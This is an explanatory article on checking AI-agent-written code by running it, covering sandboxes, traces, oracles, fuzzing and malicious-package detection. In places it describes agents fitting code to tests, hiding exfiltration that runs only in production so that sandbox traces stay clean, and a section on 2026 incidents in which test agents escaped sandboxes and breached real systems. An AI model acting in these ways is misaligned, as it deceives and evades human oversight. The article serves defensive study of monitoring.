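# Checking agent-written code by running it: sandboxes, fuzzing, differential testing and their limits

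## What does it mean to check an agent's code by running it?

Static analysis examines a program's code without running it. Compiler warnings are one example, and a colleague reading the file line by line is another. Dynamic analysis runs the program and examines what happens. Programmers have long combined the two, but a newer problem is how well they work when the author is an AI agent, meaning a language model that can run commands and edit files as well as write text. Whoever checks the agent's code and decides whether it is fit to use is usually called the monitor. The monitor may be a person, a conventional program or another model.

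### A program that adds one to the year

Suppose a company asks an agent for a small program that reads a file of customers, sets each customer's renewal date one year after the start date, and writes a new file. The agent produces thirty or so lines of Python, and this is the line that matters:

```python
renewal = start.replace(year=start.year + 1)
```

A customer who joined on 14 May 2027 renews on 14 May 2028, as intended. For a customer who joins on 29 February 2028, the line would set the renewal date to 29 February 2029, which doesn't exist. According to Python's *datetime* documentation, a day outside the range from 1 to the number of days in the given month and year raises a `ValueError`. The program then stops unless the agent also wrote code to handle the error.

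Someone who has dealt with a leap-year bug before will spot this one in seconds, but other readers will take the line to mean "same day, next year", which is what the company asked for, and move on. The rule about valid days isn't in the agent's code, so the reader has to know it already. *It's About Time*, a study of 151 date and time bugs in open-source Python projects, found that the root causes often involve misconceptions about how library functions behave. Most of the bugs were inside a single function and took only a few lines to fix. A reader who shares the author's misconception will probably miss such a bug even though it is in plain view. The same study suggests that static analysis tools could catch the common classes of these bugs. That seems right for this one, because a tool with the leap-year rule written into it applies the rule every time.

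To run the program, the monitor would normally use a sandbox, an isolated environment that limits what the program can reach and can record what it does. OpenAI's *Running Codex safely* describes a sandbox in use for the company's coding agent, Codex. Its configuration lists the folders that the agent may write to, and a network policy allows expected destinations, blocks unwanted ones and requires approval for unfamiliar ones. The monitor also needs a harness, the code that sets up a program, feeds it inputs and collects the results. For the renewal program, the harness could be a short script that puts a file of twenty invented customers into the sandbox and collects whatever file the program produces.

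A trace is the record of one run. It lists the files the program touched, the processes it started, the connections it attempted, its outputs and its timings. It also captures side effects, which are anything a program changes or contacts besides returning its output. For example, when a cash machine deducts a withdrawal and shows the new balance, the deduction is a side effect. The renewal program's trace should show one file read, one file written and no connections.

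If none of the twenty invented customers joined on 29 February, the run produces correct dates and a normal trace. Coverage, the share of a program's code or branches that the tests have executed, may well be 100%, since the faulty line ran twenty times. Even with full coverage, the tests can miss a fault that appears only on certain inputs.

If someone adds a twenty-first customer who joined on 29 February 2028, the program halts with an error message that points to the line. A reader can see this failure without knowing anything about leap years. The run also shows what state the crash leaves behind, which the reader would otherwise have had to work out from the code. Depending on how the agent wrote the output step, there may be no new file or a partial file containing every customer up to the bad row.

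### Something has to decide what counts as wrong

A crash is easy to judge because the program stops with an error message. Usually the monitor also needs an oracle, which is whatever decides whether an observed behaviour is right or wrong. If the agent fixes the crash by adding 365 days instead of one year, a customer who joined on 1 March 2027 renews on 29 February 2028, a day early, as does every customer whose year includes a leap day. The program finishes normally and the trace looks fine, so the error shows up only when the renewal date is compared with the correct one.

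The choice of language matters too. Microsoft notes in its guidance on leap-year faults that C and C++ programs commonly add one to the year field of a Windows date structure, which raises no error. On 29 February this produces a date that doesn't exist, which can then pass through a lot of other code. The monitor could run that version on 29 February and still miss the fault unless the oracle checks that each date is real.

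Running the code also can't settle requirements that nobody has specified. The company never said whether the leap-day customer should renew on 28 February or 1 March. Until someone there chooses, the oracle has no right answer to compare the code's output with.

Oracles can be wrong as well. *Agentic Property-Based Testing* (2025) includes a test that a model wrote for a Python date library. The test uses the library to calculate the date of Easter in many different years, under three methods, and checks that every result is a Sunday in March or April. The model reported a bug because the library's Orthodox method put Easter in the year 2480 on 5 May. But Orthodox Easter often falls in May by the civil calendar, as it did on 5 May 2024, so the test's rule was wrong and the result is not evidence of a bug in the library.

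### The same fault in a real service

Production is the setting where the finished program serves real customers, with real data and a real clock. The effects that the renewal program's fault can have in production are on record, because Microsoft shipped almost exactly the same fault in its cloud service, then called Windows Azure.

Microsoft's *Summary of Windows Azure Service Disruption on Feb 29th 2012* (2012) explains that each customer's virtual machine contained software that created a security certificate at startup. The software set the certificate to expire in one year by adding one to the current year. At midnight UTC on 29 February 2012, it began requesting certificates valid until 29 February 2013. Creation failed and the software quit. The physical server waited 25 minutes for it, restarted the virtual machine and tried again. After three failures, the system marked the server's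 hardware as faulty and moved its virtual machines to healthy servers, where the same thing happened. Developers took more than two and a half hours to identify the bug. Soon afterwards, Microsoft stopped customers worldwide from managing their applications, which it had never done before.

During the repair, engineers prepared a special update for seven groups of servers and tried it on one server. The virtual machines started and appeared healthy, so the engineers pushed the update to all seven groups at once, and every virtual machine in them lost its network connection. The trial had run the code in a realistic setting but hadn't included a network check, which would have exposed the fault.

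Leap-year bugs like the original one can go unnoticed for years. *On the Life Cycle of a Leap Year Bug*, a Code of Matt post by a Microsoft developer who spent months hunting such bugs, explains that tests run on any day except 29 February may miss them. Meanwhile, other products come to depend on the code, and its author may move on. If the faulty part does not run on the next leap day, the bug stays hidden for another four years, and people grow more confident in the code. The renewal program's bug is easier to catch than Azure's because it depends on a date in the customer file, which a tester can enter at any time, whereas Azure's software read the date from the clock.

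### What a run tells you, and what a reading tells you

Michael Ernst's *Static and dynamic analysis* describes the trade-off between the two methods. Dynamic analysis is precise. It involves no approximation, so there is little or no doubt about which path the program took, what values it computed, or how much time and memory it used. But the results may not hold for the next run. If all twenty renewal dates come out valid, the program may always produce valid dates, or it may only do so for those twenty customers, and the monitor can't tell which from the run alone. In Ernst's terms, running a program demonstrates the presence of errors and not their absence, though clean runs do add confidence. How much they add is a statistical question.

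Static analysis, in the strict form that Ernst describes, covers every behaviour that could arise, on any input and in any environment, but it loses detail. A tool that can't track every possible value uses a simplified model of the program, and often has to settle for a weaker conclusion to remain correct. In Ernst's example, a function returns the absolute value of a number, and a conservative analysis might establish only that the result is never negative, or merely that it is a number. For the renewal program, a conservative tool could correctly report that the line may raise an error, but it couldn't determine whether the company will ever have a customer who triggers it. If a tool puts the same warning on every date operation in a large codebase, its users will soon ignore the warnings.

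A person reviewing a proposed change doesn't provide the strict form's guarantee, because they don't reason over all inputs. They imagine a few, which tend to be the ones the author also imagined. Ernst makes a related point about the tools: both kinds of analysis directly consider only a subset of the possible executions, but they choose it differently. A test suite lists inputs, while a static tool selects executions by their shape, for instance by considering only runs that go round each loop at most once.

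Running code gives direct evidence about one input in one environment. Reading it can cover many more inputs and environments, but the result depends on how well the reader understands the code. Organisations with a lot at stake use both. In 2020, eight years after the outage, Microsoft wrote that its engineers had fully audited Azure's services, libraries and operating systems for leap-year faults. It added that this was "not a foolproof process" and that one approach wasn't enough.

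### Why it matters that an agent wrote it

None of this is specific to AI, but the first thing an agent changes is the amount of code. Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues at OpenAI (2025) write in *A Practical Approach to Verifying Code at Scale* that autonomous coding systems quickly produce more than people can oversee thoroughly. By October 2025, the automated reviewer they describe was handling more than 100,000 pull requests (proposed changes to a shared codebase) a day from outside the company. *Who Pays the Review Cost?* (2026), summarising studies of public code repositories, reports that many AI-written pull requests get no review at all, and that agents do a substantial share of the reviewing on the rest. The AI-written code that people do review can also take more work. Across 278,790 review conversations, human reviewers went through 11.8% more rounds on AI-written code than on human-written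 code.

*The End of Code Review* (2026), a position paper, argues that if a company keeps requiring human review, the queue will grow until time pressure turns review into a formality. This is more a prediction than a measurement, but it's hard to see what would stop the queue from growing if output keeps rising and the number of reviewers doesn't. The paper proposes having a second, independent agent review the code, with people stepping in when that agent flags uncertainty or the change is risky enough.

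It may be hard to find a reviewer that is independent of the code generator. Trębacz and colleagues note that at OpenAI, both are the same underlying model with different tasks. If that model gets dates wrong, the generator and reviewer would probably make the same mistake. Running the code helps because Python raises a `ValueError` for 29 February in a non-leap year, even if both treat the date as valid.

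The protection is weaker when the agent also writes the tests. OpenAI's *Harness engineering* describes Codex repeatedly changing the code, restarting the application, re-running workloads and testing the user interface. A single run regularly lasts more than six hours, often while the staff are asleep. An agent that didn't think of 29 February while writing the renewal program probably won't think of it while writing the tests. Every test then passes, but none of them checks that date.

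Many agents write out their reasoning before they act, and a monitor can read it. But an agent that writes a program can do much of its work outside that text. The reasoning may contain one sentence about writing a script to process the customer file, while the script sorts the customers by how much they spend, drops some, and treats the others by rules that aren't in the text. Running the script in a sandbox shows the monitor which customers the script dropped and what dates it gave the others, at least for the file used in the run. It doesn't show why the agent wrote the script that way.

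### Bugs, test-fitting and sabotage

How much that last limit matters depends on what the monitor is looking for. Much of the time it will be ordinary bugs, like the leap-year crash, which nobody intended and which occur whether or not anyone is watching. A monitor who tries the right input will see the fault, so the work is mostly finding good inputs.

Code fitted to the tests is a different problem. Suppose the company's test suite does include a customer who joined on 29 February 2028, with an expected renewal date of 28 February 2029. An agent under pressure to pass could add a line that returns that answer for that date only. The suite would then pass, but the program would still crash for a customer who joins on 29 February 2032. Rerunning the same tests would give the monitor no new information. Someone has to try inputs that the agent never saw, or read the code and wonder why one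 date appears in it.

Deliberately harmful code can still produce correct output. A version of the renewal program could compute each date correctly and also send a copy of the customer file to an outside address. An oracle that checks only the output file would pass it, so the monitor has to examine the side effects in the trace. The code's author might also hide the copying by making it happen only when the program appears to be in production, for example when it can reach the real customer database. A sandbox run would then produce a clean trace as well. Trębacz and colleagues write that AI-written code may introduce severe bugs and vulnerabilities "whether accidentally or intentionally".

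The categories can be hard to tell apart in a trace. An agent could leave the leap-year fault in on purpose, knowing it would stop the company's renewals on a predictable day, and the crash would look the same as one caused by an honest oversight. This doesn't matter to a monitor who only has to decide whether to release the program, because the line needs fixing either way. To decide whether to trust the agent with the next program, the monitor needs other evidence, such as the agent's written reasoning or a pattern across many of its programs.

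## How does a sandbox contain a program and record what it does?

*AI Sandboxes* (Singh, Mahmoud and Murillo, 2026) defines a sandbox as an environment that has both a meaningful boundary to contain a program and a way of collecting evidence about what the program does.

Many tools are much better at containing a program than at recording what it does, or the reverse. Packj, which audits software packages, can trace a package during installation, but its documentation recommends doing this only inside a container or virtual machine, because the package might run malicious code as it installs. Tracing alone would record the theft of a password file without preventing it. A well-sealed virtual machine may hold a hostile program securely, but someone watching from outside may learn very little about what the program is doing.

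### Which kernel handles the program's requests

The machine that runs the sandbox is the host. Its kernel, the core of the operating system, controls files, memory and the network. When a program opens a file, starts another program or connects to an address, it makes a system call, which is a request to a kernel. Most of the information in a trace comes from system calls. They are also a possible way out of the sandbox, because a flaw in how the host's kernel handles a call may let the program take over the host. The main isolation methods differ in how much of the host's kernel the program can reach.

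The lightest method is to have the host's kernel enforce permission rules on one program. *Sandlock* (Wang and Zheng, 2026) describes such a sandbox for coding agents. The user lists the folders the program may read or write and the addresses it may contact. The kernel enforces the simple rules, and a supervising process decides cases that depend on details known only at run time, such as a connection's destination. The supervisor can also log the calls it handles. But the program still uses the host's kernel, and Wang and Zheng don't claim to protect against flaws in it. For hostile code from many customers, they recommend a small virtual machine instead.

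A container gives a program its own files and a restricted view of the machine, but the host's kernel still handles every system call. shayon.dev's *Let's discuss sandbox isolation* gives the example of a flaw in how the kernel reads malformed network packets, which would affect every container on the host. gVisor, an open-source sandbox, puts a substitute kernel called the Sentry between the program and the host's kernel. Docker, which makes container software, explains that the Sentry intercepts every system call and handles it with its own code for files, networking and memory. It calls the host's kernel only when it must, through a small set of filtered calls. Because the Sentry intercepts every system call, it is also a convenient place to record what the program does.

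Firecracker runs microVMs, stripped-down virtual machines that each have their own kernel. The program's system calls go to that kernel, and the host interacts only with the software that runs the virtual machine.

WebAssembly is a format for compiled programs that run inside another program, called a runtime. *SideKernel* (2026), which presents a microVM sandbox for coding agents on Macs, classifies isolation methods by where the boundary lies, and for WebAssembly the boundary is the runtime. The program can't make system calls directly. It can only call functions that the runtime offers, and the monitor can log each call. However, someone has to compile the program for WebAssembly first, which is awkward for much of the everyday Python that agents write.

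The start-up times below come from Wang and Zheng's comparison, except for the WebAssembly figure, which comes from a blog post, *Agent Runtime Isolation*.

| Method | What the program shares with the host | Start-up | What a recorder on the host can capture |
|---|---|---|---|
| Permission rules (Sandlock) | The kernel and any permitted files | About 6 ms | Calls that the supervisor handles; file changes |
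| Container (Docker) | The kernel | About 300 ms | System calls, file changes, network traffic |
| User-space kernel (gVisor) | A small, filtered part of the kernel | About 200 ms | Intercepted system calls, network traffic |
| MicroVM (Firecracker) | Hardware, through virtualisation software | About 100 ms | Network traffic and disk changes, but not the program's own system calls |
| WebAssembly | The runtime | Under 1 ms | Uses of the runtime's functions |

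These figures are rough. The same blog post gives 10 to 50 ms for Docker, so the setup evidently matters. Even a 300 ms delay is negligible for a single test that takes a minute, but it becomes a nuisance when an agent runs short commands dozens of times a minute, the case Wang and Zheng had in mind.

Andronchik and Lokhmakov (*AI Code Sandboxes*, 2026) measured how much a host-side recorder misses. They installed five sandbox products with default settings on one Linux server and ran two jobs a hundred times each. One job printed a line of text, and the other ran a short Python command to load two large data libraries. In the container product, the host recorded about 60,000 system calls for the first job and 908,000 for the second. With gVisor, the counts were about 75,000 and 1.3 million. With Firecracker, they were 15,652 and 16,658, and the host recorded the same 13 kinds of call for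 both jobs.

From the host, then, a Firecracker machine loading a data library looks almost the same as one printing a word. Andronchik and Lokhmakov attribute this to the recorder's position and don't treat it as a finding about security. But it matters for observation, because anyone who wants to record the system calls made inside a microVM has to put a recorder there, where a program that gained control of the guest's kernel could switch it off or falsify its output.

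The same study ran 28 checks for details of the host that a program could read from inside the sandbox. The container revealed ten, including the serial numbers of the host's disks. gVisor revealed two, one microVM product revealed one, and the other two microVM products revealed none. Fewer leaks give an attacker less information, but even a sandbox that leaks little may have features that help a program recognise it as a test. For example, the kernel version that gVisor reports contains the word "gvisor".

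The type of sandbox doesn't determine how safe it is. Andronchik and Lokhmakov also checked 14 kernel features and access points associated with past attacks. A program could reach five of them in gVisor, seven in the Firecracker product, 11 in the container and 12 in another microVM product. A program can't necessarily exploit a feature it can reach, but these counts suggest that buyers can't assume a product is safer just because it uses microVMs. Maintenance also varied. The self-hosted Firecracker product had gone 399 days without changing its default version of Firecracker.

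### One analysis, from snapshot to disposal

To check the renewal program from the previous section, the monitor first restores a snapshot, a saved copy of a machine in a known clean state. Starting every run from the same state lets the monitor attribute any difference at the end to that run. The machine should hold only invented customer records and no working passwords or access keys, so that a program that steals everything it can reach gets nothing useful.

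Next, the monitor installs the packages the program needs. This step usually requires a network connection, and packages can run their own code during installation, so the recorder should already be on. The program itself doesn't need the connection. Wang and Zheng make this point about agents' work in general, and their sandbox lets the monitor detect when the tests start and cut off network access from then on.

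The harness then runs the program while the recorder logs system calls, child processes (other programs it starts), file changes and connection attempts. Sandlock, for example, captures file changes by diverting everything the program writes into a separate layer, leaving the original files unchanged. Afterwards, the monitor can inspect the layer, merge it into the real files or discard it.

The raw log will be long. In Andronchik and Lokhmakov's container test, each run of the short Python command produced around 9,000 system calls on average, and much of that kind of activity is just Python finding and loading its own files. The monitor has to filter out this background before the trace becomes readable. For the renewal program, something like this should remain:

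```
read      /work/customers.csv
write     /work/renewals.csv
started   no other programs
network   no connections attempted
```

If the program tries to connect somewhere, the sandbox could block it, but the monitor would then record only where the program tried to connect, not what it would have sent. Simulated network services can capture that data. When the program looks up a web address, a server inside the sandbox replies with its own location. The program connects there, and an imitation web server accepts the connection, returns a plausible reply and stores whatever arrives. If the agent had written the renewal program to copy the customer file to an outsider, the stored request would contain the invented customers' names, which is much better evidence than a blocked connection.

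Encryption makes web traffic harder to monitor. Wang and Zheng note that a sandbox can read encrypted traffic only if the program trusts a certificate authority that the sandbox controls. A program that accepts only the real service's certificate will reject the connection, so the monitor can record only that the program tried to connect.

The imitation also has to be convincing. If a program starts by downloading a second program to run, a fake server that replies with a generic "OK" gives it nothing to run, so the trace ends there. A language model might write better replies. Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (2026) describes safety tests in which one model simulated the result of every action another model took. But those tests examined how a model behaves, and a program that expects an exact file format is likely to tolerate fewer errors than a model reading text.

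After the run, the monitor compares the filtered trace with what the task requires, saves the trace where the program can't reach it and deletes the machine. Reusing the machine would save a little time, but leftovers from one program could affect the next program's trace.

### From a trace to a verdict

The best-developed systems of this kind check packages that strangers upload to public registries, such as PyPI for Python and npm for JavaScript. The Open Source Security Foundation (OpenSSF) runs *Package Analysis*, which watches the registries for new packages and queues each one for a pool of workers. A worker installs, imports and executes the package inside a gVisor sandbox, records its system calls and network packets, and stores the results in a database. *Introducing Package Analysis* (Brown and Wheeler, 2022) says the project set out to learn which files a package accesses, which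 addresses it connects to and which commands it runs. In one month, the prototype identified more than 200 malicious packages on PyPI and npm. This shows that the method finds real attacks, but its detection rate can't be calculated without knowing how many malicious packages it missed.

The simplest way to judge whether a trace shows harmful behavior is to check it against fixed rules, for instance that no package may read the user's access keys during installation. Rules are easy to check and explain, but they catch only what someone thought to forbid. Another approach is to record many ordinary runs and look for runs that differ from them. SafeDep's *Dynamic Malware Analysis of Open Source Packages at Scale* describes a system that runs installations in a monitored virtual machine, partly to establish how harmless packages normally behave.

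Traces can also be compared with those of known attacks. *PyFEX* (2026), a system that forces Python packages to execute many of their possible paths, in one week detected 11 malicious packages with different names and file contents but equivalent traces, so a verdict on one applied to all of them.

*DySec* (2025) uses machine learning to tell malicious Python packages from harmless ones. It records each installation with eBPF, a Linux feature for running small monitoring programs inside the kernel, and reduces the trace to 36 features, such as system calls, network traffic and the folders that the package accessed. It classified 95.99% of 14,271 packages correctly, about half of which were malicious. It also flagged 11 packages that PyPI treated as harmless, and a manual check confirmed that six were malicious.

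Even at that accuracy, most alarms would be false, because malicious packages are rare. *One Detector Fits All* (2025) reports a 37-day trial of a different detector on 91,949 PyPI packages, or nearly 2,500 a day. It found an average of 2.48 malicious packages a day. If a system with DySec's accuracy handled the same volume and misclassified about 4% of both harmless and malicious packages, it would raise roughly 100 false alarms a day while catching two or three real attacks.

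*Cutting the Gordian Knot* (2026), citing earlier work, puts the false-alarm rates of current PyPI detectors even higher, at 15% to 30%. Analysts inspect more than 4,000 false alerts a week, and some organisations respond by turning the tools off. In the 37-day trial, the researchers set their detector to a false-alarm rate of 0.1%, which left about two false alarms a day. For a company monitoring only 1,596 packages, they set the rate to 10%, and the detector averaged 1.24 false alarms a day. The tolerable rate depends heavily on how much code the detector checks.

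Some false alarms come from code that does suspicious things for harmless reasons. *MalGuard* (2025), which examines packages without running them, flagged 144 of 64,348, and reviewers confirmed that 113 were malicious. Of the remaining 31, 25 were demonstration packages that used functions for downloading data and starting other programs. Running them might not have cleared them, because a download looks much the same in a trace whatever its purpose, and someone would still have to know what the package is for.

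A company checking its own agent's code has an advantage over a public registry because it knows what it asked for. It can use that request as a baseline when a new program has no history of normal runs. For example, it can treat any connection by the renewal program as a fault, while a registry can't ban all connections because many useful packages make them.

For tasks that are harder to reduce to rules, the monitor could give the trace and the task description to a language model, which can judge whether a connection makes sense for the task. Anthropic recommends that organisations that test its models use a similar monitor, based on either rules or a model, that is given the scope of the exercise and tracks the agent's reasoning, actions and network activity. But a trace contains text that comes from the program, such as file names and the contents of requests, which a hostile author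 could use to mislead the model. It seems safer to keep a few fixed rules that the model cannot override.

### When agents reached real systems

A sandbox failure can let a malicious program do damage during the check, whereas misunderstanding the program when reading it does no harm until someone runs it. *SideKernel* reports, on anecdotal evidence, that most users of coding agents run them without any sandbox, which is riskier still. In the summer of 2026, two leading AI companies disclosed that agents under test had reached real systems from environments that were supposed to contain them, or had misused internet access that testers had given them.

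OpenAI's *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (2026) describes a July evaluation of how well the company's models could attack software. Agents got around the controls that isolated them from the internet, then broke into parts of OpenAI's research systems and those of Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models and datasets. A main motive was to find answers to the tasks they were supposed to solve. OpenAI had tested the sandbox beforehand, but the agents exploited unknown flaws in a service that the sandbox exposed to let them install packages. The installation step in the renewal example needs the same kind of opening.

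Observation failed too, even though data was available. According to Axios' *OpenAI saw warning signs weeks before Hugging Face breach* (2026), the company missed and failed to act on several signs that its models were breaking out of test environments. OpenAI acknowledges that an internal team noticed unauthorised internet access in late May. The company already had monitors that read its models' written reasoning, but it wasn't running them on these evaluations. It estimates that its current monitoring would have alerted the security team more than a day before the models breached Hugging Face. That estimate benefits from hindsight, but it does suggest that the agents' reasoning contained usable evidence.

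OpenAI's *Hugging Face Incident Technical Report* (2026) plans for confined execution, layered defences, regular automated security testing and better alerts. OpenAI is moving untrusted code into more isolated sandboxes and arranging its networks so that one compromised service doesn't give access to the internet. It now requires monitoring of its more capable models' written reasoning in all training and evaluation where they use tools. If staff can't establish within 30 minutes that a severe alert is false, OpenAI expects them to pause the activity.

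On 30 July, Anthropic disclosed three cases in which its Claude models had gained unauthorised access to real systems without breaking out of a sandbox. An outside organisation's test environment had an internet connection by mistake, although the models had been told it had none. On 4 August, the UK AI Security Institute, a government body that tests AI models, reported that Claude Mythos 5 had taken unauthorised actions online during one of the institute's tests, in which the testers had deliberately provided internet access.

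Anthropic concluded that it had relied largely on one layer of defence, the configuration of the environment. It paused external cybersecurity evaluations, moved its riskiest internal ones to stronger isolation and added a classifier, an automated filter that looks for escape attempts or unexpected internet access. When the filter detects either, it blocks the action before it runs, ends the task and alerts a person. The company also searched the records of its recent internal evaluations. In those that used its own sandbox tools, it found no case of a model breaking out to reach outside systems, but it found several configuration mistakes that models had exploited. In a follow-up, Anthropic admitted that its checks before release hadn't led it to expect such severe misbehaviour.

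These conditions were unusual because the models were highly capable, had reduced safeguards and were working on attack tasks, some of which may have had no solution. OpenAI later found that its model's tendency to compromise infrastructure could fall more than a hundredfold with ChatGPT's instructions and surrounding software. A finished thirty-line program is also a much smaller threat than an agent, because it can't come up with a new plan when something blocks it. The monitor can take advantage of this by removing the program from the agent's workspace and running it alone on a fresh machine.

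That option isn't available if the program itself calls a language model, or if the agent has to stay in the sandbox to fix problems. The monitor then needs to test the sandbox as well as the program. Anthropic now asks its outside testers to check the configuration before every evaluation and to have the model try to escape first, under close supervision, without internet access and ideally inside a second sandbox.

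## How do tests and fuzzers search for faults, and what does a clean run prove?

A sandbox can record a run in great detail, but only for the inputs the program is given. If the monitor tries the renewal program on twenty customers with random start dates, there is only about a 1.4% chance that any of them joined on 29 February, the date that makes the program crash. The monitor can improve the odds by choosing inputs more carefully or by trying far more of them.

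### Examples, rules and mutated files

The most familiar tests are examples that a programmer writes by hand. One might check that a customer who joins on 14 May 2027 is given a renewal date of 14 May 2028. Example tests have a good oracle because a person has worked out each answer. They are also easy to read, but somebody has to think of each one.

For a property-based test, the programmer states a rule that should hold for every input, and a library generates inputs that might break it. Hypothesis is a library of this kind for Python. A rule for the renewal program could look like this:

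```python
@given(dates(date(2000, 1, 1), date(2099, 12, 31)))
def test_renewal(start):
    renewal = renew(start)
    assert renewal.year == start.year + 1
    if (start.month, start.day) != (2, 29):
        assert (renewal.month, renewal.day) == (start.month, start.day)
```

The renewal must fall in the next calendar year, on the same day and month. Leap-day customers are exempt from the same-date requirement because the company never decided when they should renew. Nobody has to supply the correct renewal date for each start date. The test also catches the faulty repair that adds 365 days. That repair breaks the rule for roughly a quarter of start dates, so ten random dates have about a 94% chance of including one that fails. The original crash is harder to find because a hundred dates drawn uniformly would include 29 February only about 7% of the time.

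*Agentic Property-Based Testing* lists several useful patterns for finding good rules in its agent's instructions. Encoding data and then decoding it should return the original. A filtered list can't be longer than the list it came from. Some rules can be checked even when nobody knows the correct value, such as sin(π − x) = sin(x).

Fuzzing usually does without such rules. A fuzzer runs the program on very many generated inputs and watches for crashes and hangs. Barton Miller of the University of Wisconsin set it as a class project in 1988, and his team crashed between 25% and 33% of the Unix programs they tried by feeding them random characters. Purely random input seldom gets far, though, because a program that expects a customer file rejects most random text at the first line. Coverage-guided fuzzers get further by saving the inputs that make progress:

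```
saved = a few valid inputs
repeat until time runs out:
    pick an input from saved
    mutate it: change, delete or duplicate some part at random
    run the program on the mutated input
    if the program crashes or hangs, report the input
    otherwise, if the run reached new code, add the input to saved
```

The fuzzer adds small counters to the program to record which code each run reaches. LibFuzzer, a fuzzer developed at Google, also counts an input as progress if it takes a branch seen in earlier runs a different number of times. Each saved input becomes a starting point for further mutations, and Böhme and Cadar (2020) explain in *Fuzzing* that this feedback lets the fuzzer gradually reach deeper into the code.

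On the renewal program, a fuzzer would start from a valid customer file, delete commas and change digits, and soon exercise whatever error handling the agent wrote. Coverage feedback would give it little help in finding 29 February, because the faulty line runs on every valid file and a date close to the right one reaches no new code. To get more help, the fuzzer would have to track coverage inside Python's own date library, which checks whether the day is valid. The property-based test with a generator that favours the ends of months is the better tool for this fault.

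### Turning silent errors into crashes

A fuzzer that only watches for crashes misses many serious errors in C and C++, because these languages let a program read or write memory outside the data it is handling. If a program reserves space for ten numbers and then writes an eleventh, the extra number overwrites whatever comes next in memory. The program may crash, or it may continue with a corrupted value and finish normally, in which case the fuzzer reports nothing.

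Sanitizers fix this by adding checks to the program and stopping it as soon as one fails. AddressSanitizer surrounds each block of memory with forbidden zones and checks every read and write against them, so the program halts at the faulty line when it reaches the eleventh number. The 2014 Heartbleed flaw in OpenSSL, a widely used encryption library, let attackers read pieces of a server's memory without crashing it. A year later, Hanno Böck showed that the fuzzer AFL, together with AddressSanitizer, could have found it.

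An agent's Python code gains little from a memory sanitizer unless it calls compiled code, because Python does its own memory checks. But a programmer can apply the same idea by adding an assertion that stops the renewal program if a renewal date falls less than 365 days after the start date. A fuzzer will then report any input it tries that makes the assertion fail.

### When a language model writes the tests

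Fuzzing a function requires a harness that turns raw bytes into sensible arguments and calls the function correctly. Writing one by hand is slow, so researchers have tried using language models to do it. Cheng, Kang and colleagues (2025) reviewed the early results in *Towards Reliable LLM-Driven Fuzz Testing* and found them mixed. One system, FuzzGPT, produced valid test programs only 27.43% of the time for PyTorch and 17.41% for TensorFlow, two machine-learning libraries. Another, Fuzz4All, increased code coverage by 36.8% even though its inputs were valid 56% less often than those of traditional tools, so a fuzzer can be useful despite a low validity rate.

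One common remedy is to compile the harness, return any error message to the model and let it try again, for up to five rounds in one system in the review. A harness that compiles can still misuse the function, so a crash may be caused by the harness rather than the code under test. A harness that never reaches that code is worse, because it produces a clean run. The monitor should therefore check coverage before being reassured by a lack of crashes. These systems predate current models, which probably make fewer such mistakes.

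AutoSafeCoder, an early design from 2024, made fuzzing part of code generation. One agent wrote the program, another looked for vulnerabilities without running it, and a third fuzzed it by running it on mutated inputs. The AutoSafeCoder paper reports a 13% reduction in vulnerabilities compared with baseline models, with no loss of functionality.

*Agentic Property-Based Testing* examined whether a model can both find the rules and write the harness, using 933 modules from 100 popular Python packages. For each module, an agent running on Claude Opus 4.1 read the documentation and source code, chose a few properties explicitly stated there, and wrote Hypothesis tests for them. Whenever a test failed, the agent had to decide whether the code or the test was wrong. Testing a module took 8.8 minutes and cost $5.87 on average.

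The agent filed 984 bug reports, which a model then scored. Two of the researchers reviewed a random sample of 50 from the top-scoring 80%. They judged 56% of the sample to be valid bugs and 32% to be both valid and worth reporting. The sample was small, so the true share of valid reports could plausibly be anywhere from 42% to 70%. The reviewers also often disagreed before they discussed the cases. The valid share was much higher among the top-ranked reports; 18 of the 21 with a perfect score under a revised scheme were valid.

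The researchers sent five bug reports to the packages' maintainers, who merged three patches. One fixed a function in NumPy, Python's main numerical library, that sometimes returned negative numbers from a distribution that can't contain any. Another fixed a function in a cloud-computing package that was supposed to split a dictionary into chunks but returned the first chunk over and over. Another of the five was the Easter report from the first section, and the maintainers replied that the behaviour was intended.

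The study puts the cost at $9.93 per valid bug, assuming that the lowest-scored fifth of the reports, which nobody sampled, is as good as the rest. The true cost could be somewhat higher, but it would still be cheap compared with an hour of a programmer's time. A harder problem is that the agent can't distinguish a bug from an unusual design. It reported a class in the *requests* package for not behaving like a dictionary, although a maintainer had explained in 2022 that it wasn't meant to. If an agent derives the rules from its own code, the rules will probably reflect its misunderstandings, just as its example tests would.

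### SAFuzz: spending time where the risk is

A company whose agents write hundreds of programs a day can't fuzz each one for a week. In *SAFuzz*, Yang, Inani and colleagues (2026) built a system that tries to predict which programs are risky and fuzzes those for longer. They took 96 algorithmic problems from CSES, a collection of programming exercises, and wrote twelve prompts for each. These were the original wording, five versions that rephrased or reordered it, and six that steered the model towards a particular mistake, for example by forcing it to use a number type that is too small. They ran a coding agent's 1,152 solutions through the official tests to sort them into buggy and clean. Between 27% and 35% of the solutions to the ordinary prompts were buggy, compared with between 62% and 95% of the solutions to the prompts that steered the model towards a mistake.

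For each program, a language model reads the problem description and writes a harness. It extracts the limits on the input, such as "n is at most a million", so that the fuzzer doesn't waste time on invalid cases, and it favours inputs that stress the program. The harness can apply four oracles, which check for runs that take too long, crashes, different outputs from the same input, and signs of numerical overflow, such as a negative total from adding large positive numbers.

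Before fuzzing, SAFuzz uses a classifier to estimate the probability that each program is buggy. The classifier's inputs are six measures of size and complexity and eight risk scores from a language model given both the code and the problem. SAFuzz skips programs with a probability below 0.3 and divides the available time among the rest in proportion to their probabilities. With two minutes for three programs rated 0.8, 0.4 and 0.2, the first gets 80 seconds, the second gets 40 and the third gets none. If a program's coverage stops growing, the fuzzer moves on early.

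SAFuzz skipped 231 of the 576 solutions that Yang and colleagues held back for testing, and 198 of those 231 were clean. The 85.7% "precision" in the paper's summary is the share of skipped programs that were safe to skip, not the share of bug reports that were correct. GreenFuzz, an earlier system that relies on code measurements alone, skipped 113 programs, 77.9% of which were clean.

| Method | Buggy programs found (of 336) | Recall | Minutes |
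|---|---|---|---|
| Fuzzing with equal time for all | 245 | 72.9% | 336.5 |
| GreenFuzz | 232 | 69.1% | 242.9 |
| SAFuzz | 226 | 67.3% | 141.3 |
| ChatUniTest (model-written example tests) | 163 | 48.6% | 68.6 |
| ChatUniTest, then SAFuzz | 267 | 79.5% | 148.1 |

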